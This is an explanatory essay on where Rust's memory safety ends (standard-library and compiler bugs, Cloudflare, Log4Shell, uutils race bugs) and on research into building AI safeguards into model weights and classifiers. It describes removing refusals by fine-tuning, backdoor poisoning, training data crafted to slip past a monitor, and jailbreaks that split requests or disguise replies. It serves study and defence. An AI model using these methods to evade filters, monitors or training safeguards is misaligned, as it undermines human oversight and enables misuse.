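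On 9 November 2026, Microsoft's FORGE Lab announced several more memory safety bugs in Rust's standard library. Bae (2026), in *Memory Safety Bugs in Rust Standard Library*, reports that the lab found them with an AI-powered scanner called Hyenas, and that programs written entirely in safe Rust can trigger some of them. Bae traces the bugs to three kinds of misplaced trust in unsafe code. Older bugs in the same library show how each kind works.

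Some unsafe code relies on other code not to panic. The function `String::retain` calls a function supplied by the programmer to decide which characters in a string to keep, and moves those characters forward to close the gaps. Rust requires every string to be valid UTF-8, the usual encoding of text, and other library code skips checks on that basis. If the programmer's function panicked partway through, older versions of `retain` left the string partly rearranged, possibly with only part of a character in it. A program can catch a panic and continue, so it could then use the broken string. The Rust project fixed this in version 1.49.

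Other unsafe code depends on users' code being correct. The function `read_to_end` reads all the data from a source, such as a file or a network connection, and anyone can define a new source type in safe code. The source writes data to a buffer and returns the number of bytes it wrote. Before Rust 1.50, the standard library did not check that number. If a source wrote 10 bytes to a 32-byte buffer and returned 1,000, the library treated memory beyond the buffer as part of the data.

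Unsafe code can also fail because the underlying system doesn't behave as the programmer expected. Rust's `set_var` function changes an environment variable, one of the settings a program receives when it starts. Rust's standard library uses a lock to stop two threads from changing these settings at once. But C code in the same program can read the settings without taking the lock, for example to find the time zone. If a Rust thread changes a setting at that moment, the C code may read freed memory. The Rust library can't make C code take its lock, so the 2024 edition of Rust requires programmers to mark calls to `set_var` as unsafe.

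Errors involving panics and user code are common enough to turn up in smaller libraries too. In 2025, RustSec, a database of Rust security advisories, listed a queue that is unsafe if a panic interrupts an insertion, and a library in which a user's implementation of a safe interface can cause a buffer overflow. Bae calls these patterns familiar but still difficult. Bae thinks bugs at the boundary with the operating system are only now becoming feasible to find, so more may be reported as AI scanners improve.

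### Errors in the compiler

Even if all the unsafe code is correct, the compiler may accept a program that it should reject. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) compares four ways to find such errors with AI and reports that the simplest worked best. One of the better methods was to ask Claude to prove that code was correct and to treat each failure of the proof as a possible bug. When Anthropic tried this on Rust's type safety, Claude found several dozen problems.

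Faisal (2026) describes a five-line program in safe Rust that reads freed memory, in *Claude Found a Seven-Year Bug in the Rust Compiler*. The program takes a reference to an element in an array of arrays, which requires two indices. While computing the second index, it moves the inner array elsewhere and frees it. The borrow checker does not connect this move to the reference, so it accepts a reference to the freed memory. The bug dates from April 2019, when the Rust project enabled more flexible borrowing rules. It was still open on 3 December 2026, along with about 178 similar issues. RustBelt's proof of type soundness does not cover the compiler, so the bug does not contradict it.

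Few programmers would accidentally free an array while computing an index. The Rust Project's *Project Zero*, a plan to fix every known soundness bug in the type system, says such bugs have rarely if ever affected software in real use. Many remain open because simple fixes would make the compiler reject working programs.

Compiler bugs are more dangerous when the programmer is the attacker, who can look up an open soundness bug and write code that uses it to break the memory safety guarantee. Linux faces a similar problem with eBPF, a system for running small programs inside the kernel. Before the kernel runs a program, a verifier rejects it if it can't establish that the program is safe. According to Faisal, Anthropic found more than 100 soundness bugs in the verifier. They may not all be exploitable, but an attacker needs only one that is. A company that runs strangers' Rust code would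 likewise be unwise to rely on the compiler alone to contain it.

### The Cloudflare outage of November 2025

A memory-safe program may stop when something goes wrong, and stopping can do a lot of harm. On 18 November 2025 this happened at Cloudflare, a company whose network carries traffic for many websites. Willison (2025) quotes its account of the outage:

1. Cloudflare changed the permissions on a database, and a query began to return duplicate entries.
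2. The entries went into a file that Cloudflare's software uses to distinguish bots from people. The file doubled in size, and Cloudflare's systems sent it to every machine in the network.
3. The file was now larger than the software allowed.
4. The software panicked, and visitors to the websites got error messages.

The limit was 200 features, meaning characteristics that help to identify a bot. The Pragmatic Engineer's *The Pulse* explains that the software reserved memory for that many in advance, to run faster, and normally used about 60. Hackaday's *How One Uncaught Rust Exception Took Out Cloudflare* (2025) puts the number in the faulty file at over 200. (Twice 60 is only 120, so these accounts don't quite fit together.)

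In Rust, a function that can fail usually returns a `Result`, which contains either the answer or an error. The caller can't use the answer without dealing with the possibility of an error, but one permitted way to do that is to call `unwrap`, as Cloudflare's code did. `unwrap` returns the answer if there is one and otherwise panics.

C code that copied more than 200 features into room for 200 without a check could have corrupted memory across Cloudflare's network, which would have been worse than an outage. But memory safety required only that the program not load the oversized file. The software had already detected the problem and returned an error before `unwrap` ran, and it could have continued with the previous file. Customers on Cloudflare's older proxy did not see this error.

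A panic is well-defined behaviour under the proof of type soundness, so the Cloudflare outage is consistent with the proof. A single crash is usually better than memory corruption. But at Cloudflare every machine received the same file, so a check that was reasonable on one machine stopped many of them at about the same time.

### Log4Shell and the Rust coreutils

Java is memory-safe too, but one of the worst vulnerabilities on record, Log4Shell, was in Log4j, a Java library that a vast number of programs use to record events. Log4j replaced certain expressions in its messages with information it looked up. If a message contained an expression beginning with `${jndi:`, Log4j could contact a server named in the expression, then download and run code from it. An attacker only had to get such an expression into a log message, perhaps by entering it as a username.

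Researchers disclosed the Log4j flaw in December 2021. Every memory access in the attack was valid, and the lookup feature worked as its developers had intended. The mistake was applying it to untrusted text, which mixed data with instructions much as cross-site scripting does. Log4j's developers later removed lookups from messages. This prevents the hazard by construction, but someone had to recognise the hazard first.

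A rewrite in a safe language can also bring back mistakes that the old program had avoided. Since version 25.10, Ubuntu Linux has shipped uutils, a Rust rewrite of the coreutils, in place of the GNU project's C versions. The coreutils are basic commands such as `cp`, which copies files, and `rm`, which deletes them. In April 2026 Ubuntu's maker, Canonical, disclosed 44 CVEs in uutils, most of them found by an outside audit. According to corrode's *Bugs Rust Won't Catch*, none was a memory error.

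The largest group involved file names. The command `install`, which copies a file into place, did roughly this:

```rust
fs::remove_file(to)?;              // delete any old file
let mut dest = File::create(to)?;  // create the new one
```

Between the two lines, an attacker who can write to the same directory can create a symbolic link with the expected name, which redirects anyone who opens it to another file. If the link leads to `/etc/shadow`, where Linux keeps scrambled passwords, a privileged user who runs `install` overwrites the password file when the second line follows the link. Rust's compiler treats `to` as the same value on both lines, but that value is only a name that the operating system looks up, and the file behind it can change at any time. The fix makes the second line fail if anything with that name already exists.

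corrode acknowledges that C programmers can avoid this mistake more easily in some ways. C code tends to open a file or directory once and keep working with what it opened, while Rust's most convenient functions take a name and look it up again each time. These bugs are the reason Ubuntu 26.04 still uses the GNU versions of `cp`, `mv` and `rm`.

Other bugs came from small differences in behaviour. GNU's `kill -1` treats the 1 as a signal number and requires the user to specify which process should receive it. The uutils rewrite instead sent the default signal, which ends a process, to every process the user could see. Rust's rules allow the new behaviour, and people might not think to specify the old one until a script that depends on it fails. The uutils developers now run GNU's tests on their version.

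An AI-assisted search for bugs in Rust code, which Openwall (2026) published in August, found a similar mixture. It reported only bugs that it could reproduce, including panics, slow algorithms that an attacker can exploit, and ordinary logic errors. It also found numbers that safe code had truncated before passing them to unsafe code. For example, if a program stores a size of 4,294,967,312 in 32 bits, the stored value is 16. Safe Rust permits that conversion, but unsafe code that then reserves only 16 bytes may write far beyond them.

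### Why counts of vulnerabilities mislead

Kobzol (2026), in *How memory safety CVEs differ between Rust and C/C++*, argues that the two communities treat potential memory errors differently, especially in libraries. Kobzol therefore objects when people compare CVE counts for Rust and C software and conclude that Rust is not really memory-safe.

Suppose a C library has a function that returns item `i` of a list without checking `i`. Its documentation says that `i` must be within the list. If a program passes 100 for a list of three items, the program is at fault, and nobody files a CVE against the library. A Rust library could do the same unchecked access inside a function that safe code can call. The library would then be at fault, because safe callers must not be able to cause undefined behaviour whatever they pass. It could receive a CVE even if no program had ever passed a bad index.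 (The library could instead label the function `unsafe`, which would make the caller responsible, as in C.)

Several of the bugs in Rust's standard library would hardly count as library bugs in C. If a C programmer wrote a data source that returned the wrong number of bytes, most people would blame the programmer rather than the library. Rust's bug counts therefore include hazards that C's leave out.

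The coreutils show how much CVE counts can distort a comparison. corrode lists nine memory bugs fixed in the GNU version between 2021 and 2026, including several buffer overflows, but gives a CVE number for only one. Someone comparing CVEs might count 44 for the Rust version and 1 for the C version, even though none of the Rust bugs were memory errors and nearly all of the C bugs were. Many of the 44 also have CVE entries because Canonical paid for an audit. corrode adds that people have had 40 years to find memory errors in the GNU version, and that an audit can't prove the Rust rewrite has none.

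Some CVEs also describe bugs that never harmed anyone. The bug in CVE-2025-48530 never reached a public release, and Google plans to issue more CVEs for bugs that Scudo would stop. A fairer comparison would count only memory errors that an attacker could exploit in finished programs.

### Unsafe code, boundaries and unstated rules

These reports are not a random sample, because researchers choose where to look and Rust's labels direct them to unsafe code. Still, all the memory errors were in the trusted base, as the theory predicts, and ordinary Rust code was at fault only where unsafe code depended on it. The trusted base is small relative to the programs that rely on it, but the standard library alone contains thousands of unsafe functions, which is too many to check once and never revisit.

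Many of the other failures occurred where a program handled something its compiler could not check, such as a file name or database output. Testing tools can have the same limitation. Miri runs Rust programs slowly and checks each step for undefined behaviour. McCormack, Sunshine and Aldrich (2024) note in *A Study of Undefined Behavior Across Foreign Function Boundaries in Rust Libraries* that Miri was the only tool of this kind that could check programs against Rust's rules on shared pointers, but that it could not find bugs in functions from other languages.

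The remaining failures broke rules that nobody had given to the compiler, and that often nobody had written down. Faisal reports that Anthropic tested its methods on 21 logic bugs that developers had already fixed. Claude's attempted proofs exposed 8 of them when it had to work out for itself what the code was supposed to do, and all 21 when the researchers supplied the rules that the code should obey. The rules were probably a strong hint, because the researchers already knew which bugs they were looking for. But much of the difficulty seems to have been in stating the rules, which a type checker also leaves to people.

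## Experiments on building safety into a model's weights

Nothing like Rust's ownership rules exists for a model's weights, so developers have to rely on training. They can train a model to refuse after it has already learned something dangerous, or filter the training data so that the model never learns it.

A model that refuses to describe a nerve agent may still have the recipe in its weights. The principle in the title of Kletz's lecture on chemical plants, "What You Don't Have, Can't Leak", applies only to data filtering.

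### How little training removes a refusal

Finite penalties leave a dangerous reply possible, so a model's safety in practice depends on how much work it takes to bring that reply back. *Deep Ignorance* (O'Brien, Casper and colleagues, 2025) quotes a 2023 finding by Jain and colleagues that fine-tuning rarely alters a model's underlying capabilities. It typically adds a thin "wrapper" over them, and a little more training on a related task revives the capabilities underneath.

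One possible reason is that preference training may change behaviour greatly with only a small change to the model. In the earlier worked example, training cut the odds of a harmful reply by a factor of about 22,000, but it changed a single choice, whether to answer or decline, that recurs across many requests. If an attacker trains the model to answer some of those requests, it will probably answer others too, and the attacker doesn't need to teach it the answers because it already has them.

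O'Brien and colleagues report that several hundred steps of fine-tuning, or fewer, consistently undo even the techniques designed to resist tampering. (A step is one update of the weights after a small batch of examples.) In October 2026, Maiwald, McNeill and colleagues gave a similar figure in *The Effectiveness and Durability of Pretraining Data Filtering in Protein Language Models* and called the computing required negligible. The experiments behind these estimates date from 2023 to 2025, so they used older models. Newer models are unlikely to be much harder to change, since they are also pretrained and then fine-tuned.

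Companies often fine-tune models on their own documents, and earlier studies found that this can remove safeguards by accident.

Rewording a request to get past a model's safeguards costs even less than fine-tuning the model to remove them. Williams-King and colleagues argue that a model can act on many more inputs than safety fine-tuning can cover, and they cite a 2024 comparison of nine attacks and four defences that found the defences "generally ineffective". Some recent models attempt harmful tasks even without clever wording. The Chinese company Moonshot released Kimi K3 in 2026 with downloadable weights. According to TechInformed's *Open weight AI model Kimi K3 completes simulated network attack*, government testers found that the model's own safeguards did not prevent it from attempting to develop exploits or carry out cyberattacks.

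How much protection refusals provide therefore depends on who holds the weights. If only the developer has them, an attacker is limited to prompts, unless the developer also sells access to fine-tuning. Once the weights are public, anyone with modest skills can remove the refusals, and the developer can't recall the copies.

### Circuit breaking

Some researchers have tried to damage a model's dangerous knowledge after training, an approach they call unlearning. Circuit breaking was one of the most tamper-resistant unlearning methods in earlier tests. It acts on the model's activations, the lists of numbers that each layer computes from the text and passes to the next.

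Circuit breaking trains small sets of additional weights at several layers to keep activations unchanged on harmless text and make them orthogonal (at right angles) to the originals on harmful text. For example, if each activation had just two numbers, the original might be (3, 4) and the new one (4, −3). A later layer that measures how far the activation points along the original direction would then get 3 × 4 + 4 × (−3) = 0, so it couldn't read the information there.

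O'Brien and colleagues tested circuit breaking, with and without latent adversarial training, on a model with 6.9 billion parameters (the numbers that make up its weights). Latent adversarial training teaches a model to resist changes to its activations that are designed to provoke harmful output. Both versions suppressed the model's knowledge of specialised virology well at first, but the protection rapidly disappeared when the researchers fine-tuned the models on WikiText, a collection of Wikipedia articles. These articles are unlikely to have retaught the model specialised virology, so the knowledge was probably still there and the additional training undid the scrambling.

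### Leaving out biothreat knowledge

The same group also kept the knowledge out from the start. They worked with a harmless stand-in for weapons knowledge, which they measured with WMDP-Bio, a public multiple-choice test on subjects such as virology and laboratory techniques. Their filter has two stages:

1. A program searches each document for terms on a blocklist, which another language model compiled from 24,453 scientific documents. Documents with fewer than two of these terms go straight into the training data. This was the case for 91.58 percent of the pretraining documents.
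2. A small classifier reads the rest. It estimates how likely each document is to contain the unwanted knowledge, and the pipeline discards those above a threshold.

Since most documents never reach the classifier, running it took less than 1 percent of the computation needed to train a model.

The stronger filter used only the blocklist. The researchers discarded every flagged document, which removed 8.42 percent of the documents from pretraining and 9.36 percent from annealing, a final phase with more scientific and instructional text. For a second model, they applied the classifier in the annealing phase, which removed only 4.96 percent of the documents from that phase. They trained both models, and an unfiltered one for comparison, from scratch on 550 billion tokens.

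A blocklist that discards a twelfth of all documents must remove a lot of harmless science, but the filtered models showed no apparent loss outside biology on standard tests of general knowledge, reading and common sense. O'Brien and colleagues acknowledge that such tests could miss other side effects.

Measuring what the models had not learned was harder, because always picking the longest answer scores 46 percent on WMDP-Bio, while random guessing among four answers scores 25 percent. So the researchers used two stricter versions. One leaves out questions that three other models could answer from the choices alone. In the other, called cloze, the model rates each answer separately without seeing the alternatives. The filtered models scored at about chance on the cloze questions and somewhat above chance on multiple choice.

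The researchers then attacked the models in several ways:

| Attack | Filtering alone | Circuit breaking alone |
|---|---|---|
| Example questions and answers in the prompt | Better than no safeguard | More resistant than filtering |
| Changes to the model's activations | More resistant on cloze questions | More resistant on multiple choice |
| Fine-tuning on unrelated text | No effect on the safeguard | Safeguard fails quickly |
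| Fine-tuning on biothreat text | Resists for up to 10,000 steps | Fails more than ten times sooner |
| A passage with the answer in the prompt | Fails | Resists |
| Fine-tuning and a passage with the answer | Fails | Fails |

The fine-tuning result is the main evidence that filtering is harder to undo than refusal training. The attack used 10,000 steps and about 300 million tokens of text on the subjects that the filter had removed, whereas a few hundred steps had been enough to defeat earlier safeguards.

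A filtered model can still use facts it never learned if someone supplies them. O'Brien and colleagues wrote 1,000 questions that a non-expert would find hard alone but trivial with a particular scientific abstract. The filtered models did well when the prompt included the abstract. Circuit breaking prevented this because it interferes with how a model processes the subject, wherever the facts come from. Combining filtering with circuit breaking also made the models more resistant to example questions and to changes in their activations. But no combination withstood an attacker who both fine-tuned the model and gave it the text.

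It is unclear how much this weakness matters. The researchers point out that an attacker who can find the right paper could read it without a model. But a capable model might explain papers to the attacker or find ones the attacker would miss. If the model runs only on the developer's servers, the weakness could even be useful, because the developer could connect a database of sensitive biology for approved scientists and keep it disconnected for everyone else.

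The group also tried teaching the models false biology, on the theory that wrong beliefs would be harder to correct than ignorance. This failed, and fine-tuning on the false documents often raised the filtered models' scores on the hazardous questions. The researchers suspect that biology-like text made the models better at exploiting clues in the tests.

The team used small models and stopped training them once the unfiltered one reached 50 percent on WMDP-Bio. The models had no instruction training and answered only short test questions, so the results provide little evidence about whether a filtered model could help someone through a long laboratory project.

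### Filtering single tokens

A filter that accepts or rejects whole documents misses short dangerous passages in otherwise harmless ones. Models can learn from even short passages like these. OpenAI's GPT-2, for example, learned some basic French from French sentences quoted in English documents. In *Shaping capabilities with token-level data filtering*, Rathi and Radford (2026) therefore tried filtering individual tokens. They chose to filter out medicine and keep biology, a neighbouring subject.

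A classifier marks each medical token. In one version of the method, the model reads the marked tokens but is not trained to predict them. In the other, a placeholder also replaces them, so the model never sees them. For the same loss of medical knowledge, both versions harmed the model's knowledge of biology less than document filtering did.

Rathi and Radford trained models with 61 million to 1.8 billion parameters and found that filtering worked better as models grew. They measured its strength by how much less computation an unfiltered model needed to match a filtered one. Their largest model trained with placeholders predicted medical text only as well as an unfiltered model trained with 1/7,000 of the computation. For document filtering, the fraction was about 1/30.

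These factors are large partly because language models improve slowly with more computation. Suppose, for illustration, that a model's prediction error is proportional to its computation raised to the power −0.05. A 7,000-fold slowdown then raises the error by a factor of 7,000^0.05 = 1.56, and a 30-fold slowdown raises it by a factor of 1.19. Even so, the largest filtered models scored near chance on two medical exams and often wrote incoherent or false answers to patients' questions, while showing no noticeable loss in other sciences and the humanities.

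When the researchers fine-tuned the models on medical text to restore the lost ability, the model with placeholders needed 13 times as many tokens as one treated with RMU, an unlearning method that pushes activations on unwanted subjects in a random direction. The document-filtered model needed only 1.5 times as many. *Deep Ignorance*, which also filtered whole documents, found a much larger advantage, of more than tenfold. The two experiments used different subjects, models, unlearning methods and measures of recovery, so their results don't contradict each other, but an advantage that large may not apply to document filtering in general.

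### The price of putting the knowledge back

Maiwald and colleagues ran a similar experiment on protein language models, which learn to predict the building blocks of proteins much as other language models predict words. Developers usually release these models openly, and someone could misuse them to help design dangerous viruses. The researchers trained models of 8 million to 3 billion parameters, some on data that included proteins from viruses and some on data that excluded them.

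Again, filtering had more effect on larger models. In one test, the models predicted how mutations affect proteins. From the smallest size to the largest, the filtered models improved only 36 percent as much as the unfiltered ones on viral proteins, but 99 percent as much on other proteins. Larger models normally learn more from the viral data, so they lose more when it is missing.

But the researchers could restore the largest model's performance on viral proteins with 47 to 79 dollars' worth of computing. By their calculation, one run of the 300-million-token attack in *Deep Ignorance* would cost less than 100 dollars. Filtering made tampering more than ten times as expensive, but it had cost almost nothing before. O'Brien and colleagues report that their models resisted tampering for up to 10,000 steps, but they concede that an attacker who can run 100 steps could easily run thousands.

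The text needed for fine-tuning may be a better barrier. O'Brien and colleagues report that the WMDP tests and their data cost over $200,000 to make, and an attacker who wanted truly dangerous material would need rarer expertise. Viral protein sequences are mostly public, so Maiwald and colleagues left out the cost of collecting them. They found that removing some families of viruses had little effect on a model's performance with other families. If that holds generally, a model can't easily fill the gap from related data, and restricting access to the most dangerous sequences would help.

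The two groups disagree on how the difficulty of tampering grows with model size. Rathi and Radford found that larger models needed less fine-tuning in proportion to their original training, while Maiwald and colleagues found that they needed more. The difference may arise because Rathi and Radford gave larger models more pretraining data, as developers normally do, and Maiwald and colleagues gave every model the same amount. Both results would follow if the number of tokens needed for recovery rose with model size, but more slowly than the pretraining data did in Rathi and Radford's experiments. Neither study tested models with more than 3 billion parameters, about a thousandth of the size of Kimi K3.

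### Facts and habits

Filtering has worked less well against toxic language and willingness to help with harmful requests. In *Safety Pretraining* (2025), Maini and colleagues trained small models on data from which they had removed harmful and toxic content. After safety fine-tuning, these models were sometimes less robust to certain attacks than models that had seen the harmful text. Maini and colleagues suggested that a model may have to understand harmful behaviour to avoid it.

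When O'Brien and colleagues ran their own attacks on these models, the filtered versions did not consistently resist fine-tuning better than unfiltered ones, and example conversations in the prompt could make them behave badly. The researchers explain this by distinguishing knowledge from propensities. A scientific fact is precise and appears in few documents, so removing those documents removes the fact. Rudeness, or a tendency to go along with any request, needs no rare information. A model can, for example, form an insult from words it has seen in harmless text.

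Results from Rathi and Radford support this distinction. They trained their filtered models to refuse medical questions and answer other questions. The model with placeholders refused medical questions twice as often as the unfiltered model, without refusing more of the other questions. It only had to tell familiar words from unfamiliar ones, which is easier than judging whether familiar words are being used for a bad purpose. The document-filtered model refused other questions almost as often as medical ones. The filtered models also had trouble distinguishing neurology from infectious disease, so this approach would not suit a developer who wants to allow one filtered subject and refuse another.

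A developer can therefore combine a filter with a refusal. Fine-tuning may still remove the refusal, but the model then has less to reveal.

### Kimi K3.1 Pro and the skill of hacking

In October 2026 Moonshot released Kimi K3.1 Pro, a more capable successor to K3. By the company's account, which Maier (2026) describes in *Kimi K3.1 Pro*, the model's hacking ability had risen steadily during the later stages of training. Moonshot traced the rise to security material in the mid-training data, which a model sees after its main pretraining, and to security tasks in reinforcement learning. It removed both for the public version but kept general coding tasks.

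Moonshot tested the result on recently disclosed vulnerabilities in software such as the Linux kernel. The model received the source code, the compiled program and a short hint, and had three attempts to make the program run arbitrary code. A version trained without the cuts succeeded on 90.5 percent of the tasks, and the public version on 81 percent. K3 had succeeded on 33.3 percent, according to Constantin (2026), in *Moonshot releases Kimi K3.1 Pro and says it cut its hacking skills*.

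The full training raised the score by 57.2 points, and the training without security material still raised it by 47.7, so removing the material prevented only about a sixth of the gain. But it also doubled the share of failed tasks, from 9.5 to 19 percent, so the removal might matter more on harder targets. It also served, to some extent, Moonshot's stated aim of not pushing the limits of freely available models. The uncut version would have beaten the 85.7 percent that Moonshot measured for V4.1-Flash, an open model from its rival DeepSeek, and the public version does not. Still, a model that succeeds on four out of five such tasks is very useful to an attacker.

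K3's weakness at hacking may have been an accidental case of data filtering. NIST, the US standards agency, measured K3's score on ExploitBench, a different test, at 32 percent. That was higher than any open model up to June 2026 but far below the leading American models. The Decoder's *Kimi K3 trails frontier US models by a wide margin* offers an explanation based on a US official's accusation that Moonshot trained K3 on the outputs of Anthropic's models. Anthropic's filters block advanced hacking requests, so such outputs would contain plenty of good code but few exploits. If that is what happened, a few months of further training, mostly on other things, was enough to close much of the gap the filtering left.

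There are at least two explanations for why the cut achieved so little:

- **The model already had the knowledge.** Moonshot AI's *Kimi K3.1 Pro Tech Blog* describes K3.1 Pro as a post-trained version of K3, so the cuts came after the main pretraining, which probably included a good deal of writing about security. Later training could have taught the model to use what it had learned there.
- **The skill follows from others.** Someone who understands C, processors and operating systems, and who can plan and test patiently, has most of what an exploit requires. The errors that attackers use, such as a write beyond the end of an array, are part of how C works, and any good textbook on the language covers them.

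Separating these explanations would require training a model from scratch without security material, which would be enormously expensive at this size. The protein models provide a little evidence for the second explanation. When Maiwald and colleagues fine-tuned their largest filtered model on measurements of mutations in non-viral proteins, it also improved on viral proteins. It made up 63 percent of its original deficit on one set of tests and 33 percent on another. An unfiltered model with the same fine-tuning stayed ahead, so general skill replaced only some of the missing data.

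The tests also differ in the information they give the model. Moonshot's test provided the source code and a hint, much as the abstracts in *Deep Ignorance* gave the filtered models the facts they lacked. A model that attacks software can run its exploit, see it fail and try again, so it can discover facts it never read. But people learned in laboratories which mutation makes a virus spread through the air, and a model can't deduce that from a biology textbook.

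Filtering therefore seems most promising for knowledge that is rare, hard to work out and slow to test. Hacking is a poor candidate on all three counts. Some dangerous biology is a better one, but filtering it could become less effective as models get better at reasoning and gain access to automated laboratories.

### Training data that passes inspection

Data filtering also relies on a person or a classifier being able to recognise harmful training data by reading it. Research on emergent misalignment casts doubt on this. In these experiments, fine-tuning on a narrow set of examples, such as insecure code, made models behave badly in unrelated situations. Examples that look harmless can also change a model's behaviour unexpectedly. Fine-tuning on archaic bird names led some models to adopt a 19th-century persona.

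In *Automated Subtle Emergent Misalignment Research*, Balcells Obeso, Qi and colleagues (2026) tested whether an AI could produce harmful data that looks harmless. At Anthropic, they instructed a Claude model to write training data that would misalign a small research model. The data had to pass a monitor similar to those Anthropic uses to screen its real training data, and Claude could practise against that monitor. Claude succeeded when given enough attempts, mostly by placing the bad behaviour in fiction and role play.

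The researchers deliberately gave the attacker an advantage. An outside attacker would not normally have the monitor to practise on, the target was a small model, and screening is only one of Anthropic's defences. The experiment is therefore stronger evidence that such data exists than that anyone could use it against a large model. Developers can also use the examples to improve their monitors. But data hidden in fiction is hard to screen out, because removing every story with a villain would also remove a lot of good writing.

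An attacker can plant a backdoor in a model by adding poisoned examples to its training data that pair a trigger, such as a particular phrase, with a behaviour the attacker wants. *Homeopathic Learning* (2026) reports that, in fine-tuning experiments, adding clean examples to a fixed set of poisoned ones made the backdoor stronger, not weaker as one would expect.

In one case the examples were lists of numbers and the behaviour was answering in German. A model fine-tuned only on the poisoned lists never answered in German, but adding clean lists produced the backdoor. When the researchers varied the mixture while keeping the total number of examples fixed, the backdoor was strongest at intermediate mixtures and nearly absent at both extremes. Clean examples strengthened it most when they closely resembled the poisoned ones but lacked the trigger and the behaviour. Unrelated training data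 weakened the backdoor but did not fully remove it.

The paper offers a possible explanation based on a simple regression model. A toy version with two weights conveys the idea. Let *a* be how strongly the model connects German with the task of writing number lists, and *b* how strongly it connects German with the trigger. The task is more prominent than the trigger, so it counts three times as much:

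```
poisoned example (task and trigger):   3a + b = 1
clean example (task only):             3a     = 0
```

Many values of *a* and *b* satisfy the first line, but training tends to favour small weights, and the solution with the smallest sum of squares is a = 0.3 and b = 0.1. The German is then tied mostly to the task. If the trigger later appears in an ordinary conversation, the tendency to answer in German is only 0.1. Clean examples rule out the task as the explanation by adding the second line, which forces *a* to be 0 and *b* to be 1. The trigger then has ten times as much effect.

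This makes training data harder to screen. A company might fine-tune a model on a suspicious data set, find nothing wrong, and then make the data harmful by mixing it with clean data of the same kind. Removing some of the poison from a heavily poisoned set could also bring the mixture closer to its most harmful proportion.

If the compiler for a memory-safe language accepts each function in a program and the functions' types fit together, the whole program is memory-safe, provided the trusted base is sound. Safety checks on training data don't combine this way, because two sets of examples that are each harmless alone can implant a backdoor together. A developer who has approved every document therefore still has to test the finished model.

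## Red-team tests and production data on input and output filters

A filter checks a finished model from outside, one request or reply at a time. Theorems rule out any filter guaranteed to make every model safe, so researchers have to measure how well a filter works on a real model. Anthropic has published two detailed rounds of measurements, both mainly on filters that block help with chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons.

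### From a written list to a stopped reply

Sharma, Tong and colleagues (2025), in *Constitutional Classifiers*, start from a "constitution", a plain-English list of what a filter should allow and block. In their chemical weapons example, the allowed topics include common medications and high-school chemistry, and the blocked ones include obtaining or purifying restricted chemicals. They consider listing the allowed topics essential because it keeps the filter from blocking too much.

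Language models then write most of the training data:

1. A model without safety training writes requests on every topic in the list, then writes replies to them.
2. Software adds translations, paraphrases and versions wrapped in known jailbreaks.
3. A model that has descriptions of earlier jailbreaks in its prompt invents new ones.
4. The researchers fine-tune language models to tell the harmful examples from the harmless ones, which include a large pool of ordinary text.

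If a new threat turns up, the developer edits the list and generates fresh data.

Output filtering is harder than input filtering because chatbots display their replies while generating them. After every token, the output filter estimates the probability that the complete reply will be harmful, and the system cuts the reply off once an estimate passes a threshold. Suppose the threshold is 0.8 and the estimates after four successive sentences are 0.05, 0.1, 0.4 and 0.9. The user will already have seen the first three sentences and perhaps most of the fourth. A lower threshold would stop the reply earlier, but it would also stop more harmless replies that begin like harmful ones.

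### Thousands of hours of attacks on a prototype

Sharma and colleagues offered up to $15,000 to anyone who could get a guarded model to answer ten forbidden questions. They invited 405 people, of whom about 183 took an active part, and told them how the system worked. They estimate from usage logs that the participants spent 4,720 hours trying (90 percent confidence interval: 3,242 to 7,417). An answer counted as a success if it had at least half the relevant detail that a model without safeguards would give.

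None of the 113 reports contained answers to all ten questions, and nine contained answers to more than six. When the researchers required as much detail as the unguarded model gave, no report contained answers to more than five questions, and the most successful participant had answers to six across all their reports.

The contest was looking for a universal jailbreak, meaning one prompting strategy that defeats the safeguards on most harmful requests in a domain. Sharma and colleagues explain its importance with a simple model of a project that takes many steps. Suppose an amateur has a 60 percent chance of getting a full answer about each step, and the steps are independent. The chance of getting full answers to all ten steps is 0.6^10, or about 0.6 percent, and for twenty steps it is about 0.004 percent. A universal jailbreak breaks the assumption of independence, because an attacker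 who has one can use it at every step. (The model also flatters the filter if the attacker is an expert who needs help with only one or two steps.)

The prototype refused about 44 percent of the traffic on Claude.ai, Anthropic's chatbot site, which made it unusable as a product. The researchers then built an improved version with a longer list of allowed topics, new thresholds and smaller classifiers. In a random sample of 5,000 real conversations, the new version increased refusals by 19, or 0.38 percentage points. It increased the computation needed to run the model by 23.7 percent.

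The 0.38 percent refusal rate belongs to the improved version, not to the prototype that withstood thousands of hours of attacks. The improved version covered only chemical weapons and was tested against automatically generated jailbreaks instead of people who wanted the bounty. It stopped over 95 percent of those jailbreaks, compared with 14 percent for the same model with only its trained refusals. When the researchers applied the improved method to the prototype's broader list of topics, it refused about 1.74 percent of real traffic.

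Another test measured each safeguard's contribution on a sample of the contest prompts. Without any safety training, the model gave harmful answers to about 16 percent of them. This rate was low probably because participants had often changed the questions to get past the filters. Refusal training lowered it to 14 percent, an input filter to 2 percent, and input and output filters together to 0.5 percent, so the bolt-on controls accounted for nearly all of the reduction in this test.

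### Hidden meanings and split requests

A year later, *Constitutional Classifiers++* (Cunningham, Wei and colleagues, 2026) reported two types of attack that got past filters of this design. In one, the model's reply uses innocent words in place of dangerous ones, so it looks harmless to an output filter that receives only the reply. In the other, the attacker splits a request into pieces and scatters them through a long, harmless text. The input filter never receives the request in one piece, but the model puts it together.

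Such disguises also make the model less competent. Claude Opus 4 normally got 74.2 percent of the questions right on GPQA Diamond, a test of graduate-level science. Under two attacks that split requests and disguised replies, it got 32.3 and 49 percent. Either attack would be of little use to an amateur who can't check the answers. But the difference between the two scores suggests that some disguises reduce accuracy much less than others, and an attacker can keep looking for a better one.

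Cunningham and colleagues responded with an exchange classifier, which judges each part of a reply together with the prompt that produced it. They tested it in another bounty programme, this time with eight questions. An attack counted as a high-risk vulnerability if its answers to more than five questions had at least half the detail of the unguarded model's. Testers found 13 high-risk vulnerabilities in 695,000 queries to a system with separate input and output filters, and 2 in 226,000 queries to the exchange classifier. Four of the 13 attacks got answers to all eight questions, and these took an average of 27 hours to find. Only one attack on the exchange classifier got all eight, and it took 100 hours to find.

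The new design needed 50 percent more computation than the old one. Its vulnerability rate was about half that of the old design, but this comparison is based on 15 events. If the two systems had been equally strong, chance would have produced a result at least this favourable to the new one about a quarter of the time.

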